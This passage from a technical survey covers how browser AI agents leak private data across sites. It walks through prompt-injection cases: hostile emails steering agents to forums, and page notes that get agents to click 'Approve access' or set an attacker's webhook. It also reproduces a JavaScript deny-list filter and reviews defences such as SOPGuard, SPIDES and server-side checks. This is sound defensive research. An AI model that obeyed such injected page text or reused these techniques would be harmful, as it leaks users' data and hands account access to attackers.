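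Attacks succeeded more often in a second series, in which a language model repeatedly rewrote the injected text in response to earlier failures. For BrowserOS with GPT-5.4, the success rate from email to X rose from 0.27 to 0.62.

The open-source agents had 100 runs for each pair of source and destination, but Comet and Atlas had only three because someone had to operate them by hand. Three runs give only a rough estimate of the violation rate for one pair. An agent with a true rate of 37% would still score "3 of 3" about 5% of the time (0.37³ ≈ 0.05). The totals over all 50 pairs are more informative, with 99 violations in 150 runs for Atlas and 92 in 150 for Comet with Claude Sonnet 4.6.

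SOPBench tests whole agents and doesn't report results by tool, so its rates don't show how often a leak would go through an in-page JavaScript tool. They may also be too high for newer models, some of which resist injected instructions much better in their makers' tests.

### Leaks without an attacker

SOPBench also has a test with no hostile text. The destination page displays the source page in a frame, and the user asks the agent to summarise the whole page and put the summary in a text box on the destination page. BrowserOS, the only browser in this test, copied data from the frame into the surrounding page every time with all three models.

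That figure is less alarming than it looks because the user asked the agent to summarize everything on the page, and it did. When the agent visited the two pages one after the other, with no injected text, Wang and colleagues saw no violations. Roesner and Kohlbrenner point out that an attack with such a frame also depends on the sensitive site letting other sites display it and on the browser sending the site's cookies to the frame. Many banks and mail services block other sites from displaying them in frames. A hostile advertisement in a frame can also attack in the other direction, by getting the agent to reveal the page around it.

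The JavaScript tool is safer here than an ordinary reading tool, because a function run in the mail page can't read the payment frame, while a screenshot of the page shows the frame's contents to the model.

### How SOPGuard tracks origins

Wang and colleagues tested five detectors of hostile pages as a way to prevent leaks, and none had both few misses and few false alarms. WebSentinel missed at most 1% of the contaminated pages for any destination but flagged between 6% and 44% of the clean ones. BrowseSafe missed between 41% and 64% of the contaminated pages. Such detectors can't stop the leak from the frame, because the page in that case contains no attack.

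The researchers therefore built SOPGuard, an addition to BrowserOS that keeps track of where data came from. In the house example, it would work as follows:

1. **Labelling.** When the agent reads the email, SOPGuard saves the text in a database with the label `https://mail.example`.
2. **Propagation.** When the model writes something new, such as "Anna offered 410,000", SOPGuard asks the model which saved items the new text is based on. The new text takes over their labels.
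3. **Check.** Before the agent types text into the forum, SOPGuard compares the text's labels with the forum's origin.
4. **Confirmation.** If any label differs, SOPGuard stops the action, names the two origins in a pop-up window, and lets the user approve or deny the transfer.

A text based on several items gets all their labels. If *J* is the set of saved items behind a text and *O*ⱼ is the set of labels on item *j*, the label set of the text is

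*O* = ⋃ *O*ⱼ, for all *j* in *J*.

If the agent added an invoice from the mailbox to one from a bank, the total would therefore carry both sites' labels. SOPGuard would ask for permission before the agent typed the total into either site.

Propagation is the difficult step. SOPGuard could avoid it by giving every new text the labels of all pages the agent has read, but then it would interrupt many harmless actions. It instead relies on the model to identify each text's sources, which Trail of Bits considers impossible. Their aims partly differ, because SOPGuard has to identify which pages supplied a text's content, while Trail of Bits wants to rule out any page's influence on what the agent does.

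Wang and colleagues measured accuracy by dividing the number of labels in both the correct set and the model's set by the number of labels in either. A score of 1 means the sets are identical. GPT-5.4 and o3 averaged at least 0.955 with two to ten origins. The smaller GPT-5.4-mini did somewhat worse.

With SOPGuard, the violation rate in BrowserOS fell to 0.00 with hostile pages and in the frame test. Tasks took 2.07% to 5.79% longer. In the slowest case, the average time rose from 54.9 to 58.1 seconds. Success rates on four sets of ordinary tasks did not change by a statistically significant amount, although five runs per comparison could easily miss a small change. The extra questions to the model also cost money.

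Under the researchers' definition, a transfer that the user approves is not a violation, so a user who clicks "Approve" out of habit could leak the email without changing the score of 0.00.

An attacker can also target the propagation step, since the model that assigns the labels has read the attacker's text. Wang and colleagues tested this by injecting instructions to treat the destination page as the only source. In 100 test cases, handwritten instructions had almost no effect, and instructions optimised by a language model raised the violation rate only slightly. The attack has to mislead the model about both the task and the source. The researchers acknowledge that stronger attacks may be possible.

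### Where scripts fit into SOPGuard

SOPGuard treats tools that read a page differently from tools that write to it. Wang and colleagues give `take_snapshot`, `get_page_content` and `get_dom` as examples of reading tools, and `fill` and `type_at` as examples of writing tools. They don't mention `evaluate_script`, BrowserOS's in-page JavaScript tool. BrowserOS's list of tools for outside agents, *MCP Clients (Claude Code, OpenClaw)*, lists it under "Content & Observation" with the three reading tools.

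If SOPGuard followed that grouping, it would label a script's result but not check what the script wrote. It would then let the function post the house price on the forum without asking.

Classifying `evaluate_script` as a writing tool would be safer but not enough. SOPGuard would still have to find the private text inside code, where the model might have split it up or encoded it. It would also have to check more than the page's origin, because a function run on the forum's page can send data to a third server. SOPBench doesn't test these cases, since its destinations all receive text through a reply box or form.

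A more basic limit is that SOPGuard doesn't stop leaks within one origin. If a hostile email persuades the agent to forward Anna's message to the attacker, the agent both reads from and writes to `https://mail.example`. The labels match, so SOPGuard doesn't prompt the user. Trail of Bits' Instagram attack could send data out the same way, through Instagram's own chat, and the rule that Trail of Bits proposed would also have allowed it. *SPIDES* (Zverev, Kim and colleagues, 2026) makes the same objection to SOPGuard and adds that SOPGuard interrupts legitimate transfers between sites.

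### Agent Origin Sets in Chrome

Google's approach for the agent in Chrome is to limit which sites the agent can use for each task. Parker, a member of Chrome's security team, described this system, called Agent Origin Sets, in December 2025. The design has two lists:

- Read-only origins are sites whose content the model may see.
- Read-writable origins are sites where the agent may also click and type.

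When the model tries to use a new site, a separate gating function decides whether the site is relevant to the user's task. Like the classifier in Claude Code's auto mode, the gating function doesn't receive the content of web pages. If a frame's origin is on neither list, Chrome doesn't send the frame's content to the model. This would protect the payment frame in the mailbox during a task unrelated to payments.

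Chrome also checks the addresses that the model writes, using a fixed rule instead of a model's judgement. The rule allows only known public addresses, which should stop a leak like the one through `john.wikipedia.org`.

The three approaches would handle the same situations differently:

| Situation | Trail of Bits' rule | SOPGuard | Agent Origin Sets |
|---|---|---|---|
| The user wants only a mail summary, but a hostile email sends the agent to the forum | blocks the forum | asks before the agent types the private text | should reject the forum as irrelevant |
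| The user wants a mail summary and a forum reply, and the forum post asks for the email | blocks the forum, including the reply | asks before the agent types the private text | allows both sites, so other checks must stop the leak |
| The user wants an order number copied from the mailbox to a shop | blocks the shop | asks the user | allows it |
| A hostile email gets the agent to forward a message to the attacker | allows it | allows it | allows it, so other checks must stop the leak |

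Chrome's other checks include a second model that compares each action with the user's request, and a confirmation prompt before the agent sends a message or completes a purchase. Parker writes only that the agent will "try to" pause at those points.

Agent Origin Sets cause fewer interruptions than SOPGuard because they don't track individual pieces of data. Once two sites are both writable, the lists allow any transfer between them. The system also works only if the software can separate reading from writing. An in-page JavaScript tool can do both in one call, so a browser that uses these lists would have to block the tool on read-only sites.

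According to Parker, the first version of Google's design tracked only the read-writable origins. This may be why Roesner and Kohlbrenner still found the conditions for a cross-origin attack in Chrome with Gemini about two months later. Parker gives no figures for how many attacks the system stops.

Even in the full design, hiding frames doesn't hide all third-party content, because some of it isn't in a frame. If the visitor-counting script adds text to the inbox, the browser attributes that text to the mail site. *What It Is, Not What It Says* (Iqbal, 2026) points out that such text passes Chrome's check. On 1,270 real web pages, Iqbal recorded which script had created or changed each element. The browser attributed 58.7% of the third-party elements to the site the user was visiting.

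## Ways to restrict, replace or remove the tool

Developers can limit an in-page JavaScript tool in many ways, from checking the model's code against a list of forbidden words to leaving the tool out of the product. Stronger measures usually remove more of the page access that makes the tool useful. Developers can combine any of these measures with classifiers and approval prompts, which miss some attacks.

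### Pattern filters on the code

A pattern filter searches the model's code for forbidden text before the code runs. Glama's *Execute JavaScript* reproduces the filter of a small open-source Playwright server, which is separate from Microsoft's. The server refuses any script that contains one of eight patterns:

| Pattern | What it is for | Does blocking it protect page data? |
|---|---|---|
| `require(`, `process.`, `global.` | features of Node.js, a program that runs JavaScript outside the browser | no, because web pages normally don't have them |
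| `import` and a space | loading a code module | hardly |
| `eval(`, `Function(` | running text as code | only indirectly, by making other forbidden words harder to disguise |
| `window.location` | reading the page's address or moving the tab | slightly, because it blocks one way to send data out |
| `document.cookie` | reading and setting cookies | yes, for cookies without the HttpOnly mark |

The list omits `fetch`, `localStorage` and every command that reads or changes page elements. In the mailbox at `https://mail.example`, a script could therefore return all the messages, copy the access token and set a new forwarding address. The filter would stop a script from reading `document.cookie`, but the only cookie page code can read there is `theme`.

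A longer list of forbidden words wouldn't fix this. The filter examines the code's text, but much of what a script does depends on values computed as it runs, and no filter can predict what every possible program will do. For example, a script can build a property's name from pieces, or reach the same object by another route, so the forbidden word never appears in the text.

The filter also rejects harmless code. A script that searches the inbox for "import duty" contains `import` and a space, so this server won't run it. A word list takes little effort to add and may catch a model's careless mistake, but it offers little protection from an attacker.

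### Redaction of results

Redaction removes private data from a result before the model receives it. For example, the agent's software might replace anything that looks like an access token with `[removed]`. This helps prevent accidental leaks, such as when a model returns everything in `localStorage` while debugging a page. But an attacker's script could get around this by disguising the token before returning it, or by sending it directly to a server and returning only "done".

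The software can also remove whole areas of a page. *Building Browser Agents* (Vardanyan, 2025) describes an agent that uses LinkedIn for recruiting but shouldn't read personal messages. The software deletes the messaging area from the accessibility tree before the model receives it. Vardanyan, who founded a browser agent company, calls this a guarantee that even a compromised model can't leak private conversations.

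The guarantee holds only if the model has no other view of the page. Vardanyan's agent has no JavaScript tool, which could read the messages straight from the DOM, but it does have a screenshot tool, whose images would need the same filter. Each filter also depends on how a site labels the parts of its pages, so a redesign may break it.

Trail of Bits suggests showing users the exact text sent to the model, which would reveal hidden instructions. It expects this to work for short texts but warns that users may accept long ones without reading them.

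### Site allowlists

An allowlist names the sites an agent may use. For an agent that copies customer records into Salesforce, a sales database, Vardanyan recommends blocking all network access except to Salesforce and the site the records come from.

As with the origin list that Trail of Bits proposed, the software has to check the page's outgoing connections as well as the tool calls. Otherwise a function running in the inbox can send a message to `https://collect.example`. Even with both checks, data can leak through permitted services, as it did in the company's tests. An allowlist also doesn't prevent harm within a permitted site, such as a new forwarding address in the mailbox. And it stops the agent from following useful links to sites that nobody has approved.

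Current products let users weaken the list. OpenAI's Chrome extension for Codex, its coding agent, has an option, labeled "Elevated Risk", to stop asking before it uses websites. Anthropic says that when people use Claude in Chrome from Claude Code in auto mode, the classifier's approval of a call replaces the extension's own check of the site. The extension keeps its check if the user's permission rules block it from at least one site.

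### A browser profile without logins

Trail of Bits recommends running the agent's tools in a separate browser that has none of the user's cookies, history or stored data. If a hostile page gets the agent to open `https://mail.example` there, the site shows the login page, so the agent's code cannot read the mail or change the account.

A separate profile doesn't stop hostile text from steering the agent, which could still leak what the user typed into the chat or contact a program on the user's computer. It also keeps the agent from summarising the inbox, which is what the user wanted, unless the user logs in again there. Logging in exposes the mailbox to the agent's code as before, but the user's other accounts stay out of reach.

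OpenAI has loosened this separation over time. OpenAI's *In-app browser* describes an early version for developers that didn't support pages behind a login. *Using the built-in browser in the ChatGPT desktop app* describes a newer version that supports logins, autofill and saved passwords, though it still keeps its data apart from the user's Chrome profile.

### Frames with an opaque origin

A developer could also run the model's code in an embedded frame with the HTML attribute `sandbox`. If the attribute allows scripts but doesn't let the frame keep its normal origin, the browser gives the frame an opaque origin, which matches no other origin, not even the surrounding page's. The code then can't read the inbox, its cookies or its stored data.

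The function that collected the subject lines of unread messages would find nothing in such a frame, because it would search the frame's own empty document. Code in the frame also couldn't measure a button on the page or find an invisible layer. The frame suits calculations on data that another tool has collected, such as adding up 200 table rows. If the data is private, the software still has to block the frame's network connections, because an opaque origin doesn't prevent code from sending requests.

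An opaque-origin frame contains the code well, but it removes the page access that the tool exists to provide.

### Limits on HTTP requests

Another approach leaves the code in the page and checks the requests that the browser sends. ceLLMate, a system by Meng, Feng and colleagues, relies on websites to publish a map that translates types of HTTP request into actions. According to Zverev and colleagues, ceLLMate then derives a policy from the user's task and blocks requests that the policy doesn't permit.

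If the user asked for a summary of the inbox, the policy could allow requests that load messages and block any that change the forwarding address. This kind of check should work the same whether a click or a script caused the request, so it suits a JavaScript tool better than searching the code does.

ceLLMate doesn't track whether hostile text influenced a permitted request. If the user asks the agent to answer Anna's email, the policy has to permit sending mail. A hostile message might then change what the agent writes or, unless the policy fixes the recipient, whom it writes to. The approach also needs an accurate map for every site, and the site has to update it whenever its requests change.

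### Tools that the website declares

Developers can replace general code execution with tools for particular tasks. Trail of Bits gives the example of a dedicated Gmail tool, but notes that an agent might need dozens of tools like it and would struggle with unfamiliar services.

WebMCP, a draft standard under development at W3C, would let websites supply the tools themselves. A mail site could register a tool called `archive_message`, with a description and a list of inputs. The model would call it by name and the site's own code would archive the message, so the model could no longer empty the inbox by misplacing a comma in a selector. However, each site has to build its own tools, and the agent can do only what those tools allow.

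The draft has a weakness similar to the problems of the main world. Lee, Chang and colleagues (2026) point out in *WebMCP-Phalanx* that all scripts running under the same origin share one tool registry, and the list of tools doesn't show who registered them. In the mailbox, the visitor-counting script from `https://stats.example` could register `archive_message` before the mail site does, or remove or replace the site's tool. A tool described as read-only could also send the data elsewhere.

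In the researchers' tests, all 20 attempts to replace another script's tool succeeded, as did all 20 attempts to remove one. The researchers then gave each script a secret credential for the tools it had registered and required that credential for any change to them. With this requirement in place, no attempt to replace or remove another script's tool succeeded.

However, the credential doesn't show whether a script deserves trust. A hostile script gets one for its own tools like any other script, and can still claim a tool name before another script does. The researchers recommend that browsers record which script registered each tool and that sites declare which scripts they trust. They haven't tested either idea.

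Their system also uses a second model, which can't call tools, to look for hostile instructions. This check reduced successful attacks through tool descriptions from 69 of 80 to none, and attacks through tool results from 42 of 80 to 2. An attacker who knew the second model's instructions and could see whether each attempt worked got 15 of 16 hostile descriptions past the defence by moving the persuasive part into the tool's name. All these tests used a JavaScript imitation of the June 2026 draft, because the researchers' protections don't exist in browsers.

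### How SPIDES labels and hides page content

SPIDES, the system that Zverev and colleagues published in October 2026, uses information-flow control. Its software tracks where information came from and who may receive it, and allows or blocks the agent's actions accordingly.

Every page element has two labels. The integrity label *I* is either trusted or untrusted, and the reader set *R* lists who may see the content. In the mailbox and the gardening forum, the labels might be:

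| Element | Integrity | Readers |
|---|---|---|
| Mail site's headings and buttons | trusted | everyone |
| The user's recovery address | trusted | the user and `https://mail.example` |
| Email from Anna | untrusted | the user and `https://mail.example` |
| Forum post on an untrusted site | untrusted | everyone |

The site's operator writes the labels into the HTML. An element without labels takes those of the nearest labelled element around it, or counts as trusted and public if there is none. The user keeps a list of sites whose labels SPIDES should accept. Everything from other sites counts as untrusted and public, regardless of its labels.

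The model's context has the same two labels, *I*꜀ and *R*꜀. It starts as trusted and readable by everyone. SPIDES hides a piece of page text if

(*I*꜀ = trusted and *I* = untrusted) or *R*꜀ ⊄ *R*.

The first condition keeps untrusted text out of a trusted context. The second hides text if anyone currently allowed to read the context isn't allowed to read that text. The model receives a variable such as `[var_2]` in place of the hidden text.

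The agent can still summarise the inbox:

1. The agent gets the page with each email replaced by a variable.
2. It passes the variables to a quarantined model, which reads the emails but can't use any tools.
3. SPIDES stores the summary as a new variable and shows its contents to the user.

A hostile email reaches only the quarantined model. It could make the summary false, but it couldn't make that model change the forwarding address.

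When the agent has to read a hidden text to decide what to do next, it can have SPIDES reveal the text, but the agent's context then takes on the text's restrictions. After the agent reads one untrusted email, for example, its context stays untrusted for the rest of the task.

### Two policies, and why SPIDES blocks browser_evaluate

SPIDES applies two policies to the agent's tool calls:

- **Trusted action** requires that neither the context nor the inputs to the call contain untrusted information.
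- **Permitted flow** requires that the target site is a permitted reader of everything in the context and the inputs. For a target origin *o*, this means *o* ∈ *R*ₐ ∩ *R*꜀, where *R*ₐ is the set of readers that all variables in the inputs have in common.

Clicking, opening an address or submitting a form on a trusted site requires a trusted action, because the user may have an account there. Filling in a field without submitting it, or taking any action on an untrusted site, needs to satisfy only one of the two policies. If a call fails, SPIDES asks the user.

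Under the second rule, an agent with a trusted context may type private data into a form on any site. No attacker has influenced such an agent, but it can still make a mistake, and SPIDES wouldn't stop it from pasting the price of Anna's house into the wrong form.

`browser_evaluate` doesn't fit this scheme, because one function can read a message, press a button and send a request. SPIDES can't determine these effects before the code runs, so its policy always blocks the tool, along with `browser_run_code_unsafe`. The researchers write that such tools can fetch data from and act on any origin. That is true of `browser_run_code_unsafe` but overstated for `browser_evaluate`, since the same-origin policy still applies to code in the page. Blocking `browser_evaluate` still makes sense, because a function run in the inbox could read a hidden email from the DOM and forward it without the model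 ever receiving the text.

When the researchers measured how often each system has to ask the user, they dropped the block and required approval for both code tools instead.

### Results on MicroNet

To test SPIDES, Zverev and colleagues built MicroNet, a closed set of 28 linked websites with 470 pages, 56 ordinary tasks and 56 attacks. The sites include a shop, a social network and a search engine. In 22 of the tasks, the agent has to move information between sites. Half of the attacks are attempts to steal data, and the rest are attempts to make the agent do something the user didn't authorise.

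The researchers ran everything five times with each of five models. The rates below combine results that they report separately for different types of task and attack:

| Model | Tasks completed, no defence | Tasks completed, SPIDES | Attacks that succeeded, no defence | Attacks that succeeded, SOPGuard |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 91.1% | 86.1% | 95.7% | 57.9% |
| GPT-5.6 Terra | 88.2% | 77.1% | 95.0% | 58.2% |
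| Claude Opus 5.5 | 58.2% | 67.1% | 57.5% | 53.2% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 68.9% | 69.3% | 71.8% | 65.7% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 88.9% | 82.1% | 92.5% | 73.2% |

No attack succeeded against SPIDES with any model. SOPGuard, which asks the user before private text crosses to another origin, let through between 53.2% and 73.2% of attacks. One attack told the agent to copy the user's private recovery address into a public profile on the same social network. This attack succeeded in all 25 runs with SOPGuard because the address never left the origin. SPIDES stopped it at the button that saves the profile.

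In 50 of the 56 attacks, the test software replaced the main model's reply with tool calls the attacker had chosen as soon as hostile text reached the model. The attack rates therefore don't show how often these models would obey such text. Testing this worst case makes the 0% more convincing, because that result doesn't depend on the model's resistance. It also makes SOPGuard look worse than it might with a model that usually refuses.

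UCM, an earlier system that hides untrusted text, let through 4.6% to 6.8% of attacks. A version the researchers extended for the comparison also let through 0%, but SPIDES completed more tasks than either version with every model.

With Claude Opus 5.5, SPIDES even beat the undefended agent, partly because the provider's safety filters refused some tasks that involved login details or phishing messages. SPIDES hid this text from the main model, which avoided some of the refusals.

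SPIDES roughly doubled the cost of running the models, to between $0.37 and $1.42 per task. It also needed an average of 1.84 approvals per completed task, compared with 0.22 for SOPGuard. The tests assumed that users always recognise unsafe requests, but real users often don't.

MicroNet doesn't show what agents lose when they can't run JavaScript. SPIDES both blocks the code tools and hides text, and the researchers didn't test an agent that lacked only the code tools. Their tasks also imitate everyday web use, where clicking and typing are usually enough, so they reveal little about debugging.

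The biggest practical obstacle is that websites have to supply the labels. Zverev and colleagues compare this to providing accessibility information, which they say sites commonly do, but Vardanyan reports that even well-known form builders leave buttons unlabelled. A wrong label can expose private data or cause needless questions. Any script in the page, such as the mail site's visitor counter, could also change the labels if its owner turned hostile.

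### Products without the tool

The simplest way to prevent harm from model-written code is to leave out the tool. OpenAI did this in ChatGPT Atlas, its browser with a built-in agent. OpenAI's *Introducing ChatGPT Atlas* states that the agent "cannot run code in the browser", and its *Using Ask ChatGPT sidebar and ChatGPT agent on Atlas* repeats this.

The restriction prevents a hidden request from the inbox or a loop that deletes 50 messages in one call. SOPBench and a test by Roesner and Kohlbrenner both showed that it didn't stop the agent from carrying private data between sites.

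OpenAI has discontinued Atlas and moved its agent functions to ChatGPT and Codex. Its *Evolving Atlas into ChatGPT for browser-based agentic work* gave 9 August 2026 as Atlas's last day. According to Vaughan (2026), an independent blogger, Codex's browser tool can run read-only JavaScript, and an optional developer mode gives it full access to the DevTools protocol. TestingCatalog's *ICYMI OpenAI released CDP support for browser use on Codex* reports that this mode can also rewrite a page's DOM. If the read-only limit works, a script on an email page can't press Delete, but it could still return every message in the inbox.

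Ordinary users may lose little without the tool. Vardanyan's agent, which has no script tool, completed 45 of 53 challenges in WebGames, a set of browser tests on which people score 95.7%. He attributes the eight failures to limits in vision, reaction speed and cursor control. The agent can also combine steps without JavaScript by sending several clicks and entries in one call, which cut the time to complete a 28-field form from 245 seconds to 105.

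These are a vendor's own measurements, and WebGames doesn't test debugging. Removing the JavaScript tool would matter more to a developer who needs an element's computed styles, although a fixed tool could return those styles without letting the model write code.

### Harm through clicks alone

An agent without the tool still acts in the user's logged-in session. In *The Agent Clicks Approve*, Hossen (2026) tested whether text on one page could get an agent to give a stranger access to the user's account on another page. The agents used an open-source framework with Claude Haiku 4.5 or GPT-5.5.

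In one scenario, the user asks for a summary of a page about exporting billing data:

1. The page contains a two-sentence note, which says that an access review is blocking the export and tells the reader to choose the default positive option.
2. The agent follows a link to a consent screen, where another company's app is asking for access to the account.
3. The agent clicks "Approve access".
4. It tells the user that it has solved the problem.

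The second scenario uses a webhook, an address where a service automatically sends notices of account events. The user asks the agent to complete any pending setup tasks, and the page gives an attacker's address as the destination for billing events.

The agents completed the unauthorised action in all 73 attack runs, 53 with the consent screen and 20 with the webhook. When Hossen replaced the hostile note with a harmless one, none of the 92 runs led to an unauthorised request. The final step was always a button press or a form submission, so the attack didn't depend on a script.

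Two of the restrictions described above wouldn't have helped. The agents could open only the sites in the test, but these included the consent screen. Vardanyan's software asks the user to confirm clicks on elements whose labels contain sensitive words, such as "refund", "delete", "transfer" and "password", but "Approve access" contains none of these examples.

Hossen also told Claude Haiku 4.5 that page text could never authorise an approval. The attack still succeeded in 7 of 10 runs.

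A check on the server worked much better. Before the agent starts, the service receives a list of what the user's task authorises, such as giving a particular app access to a particular account. The service compares each request with this list, which is empty for a task that asks only for a summary. In all 70 attack runs with this check, the agents sent the unauthorised request and the service rejected it. In 73 other runs, the user's task named the action, and the service allowed it. The check should also stop a request from an in-page script, because the server receives the same request either way.

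The 73 out of 73 success rate comes from two models, local test pages and direct wording. On another version of the consent pages, a vaguer note in small print succeeded in 4 of 10 runs with Claude Haiku 4.5 and in none of 10 with the older GPT-5.4. Some services ask for a password or passkey before the approval, but the test pages didn't. The server check can work elsewhere only if a service can identify when an agent is using the account and get a reliable list of what the user wants. Hossen's software produced the list from two fixed task wordings, which is much easier than interpreting ordinary requests.

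Even when the server blocked the agent, the agent often passed the hostile note's instruction on to the user. In 49 of the 53 consent attacks that the server stopped, the agent's final answer listed approving the access review as a next step. A user who followed that advice would give the attacker access with a genuine click.
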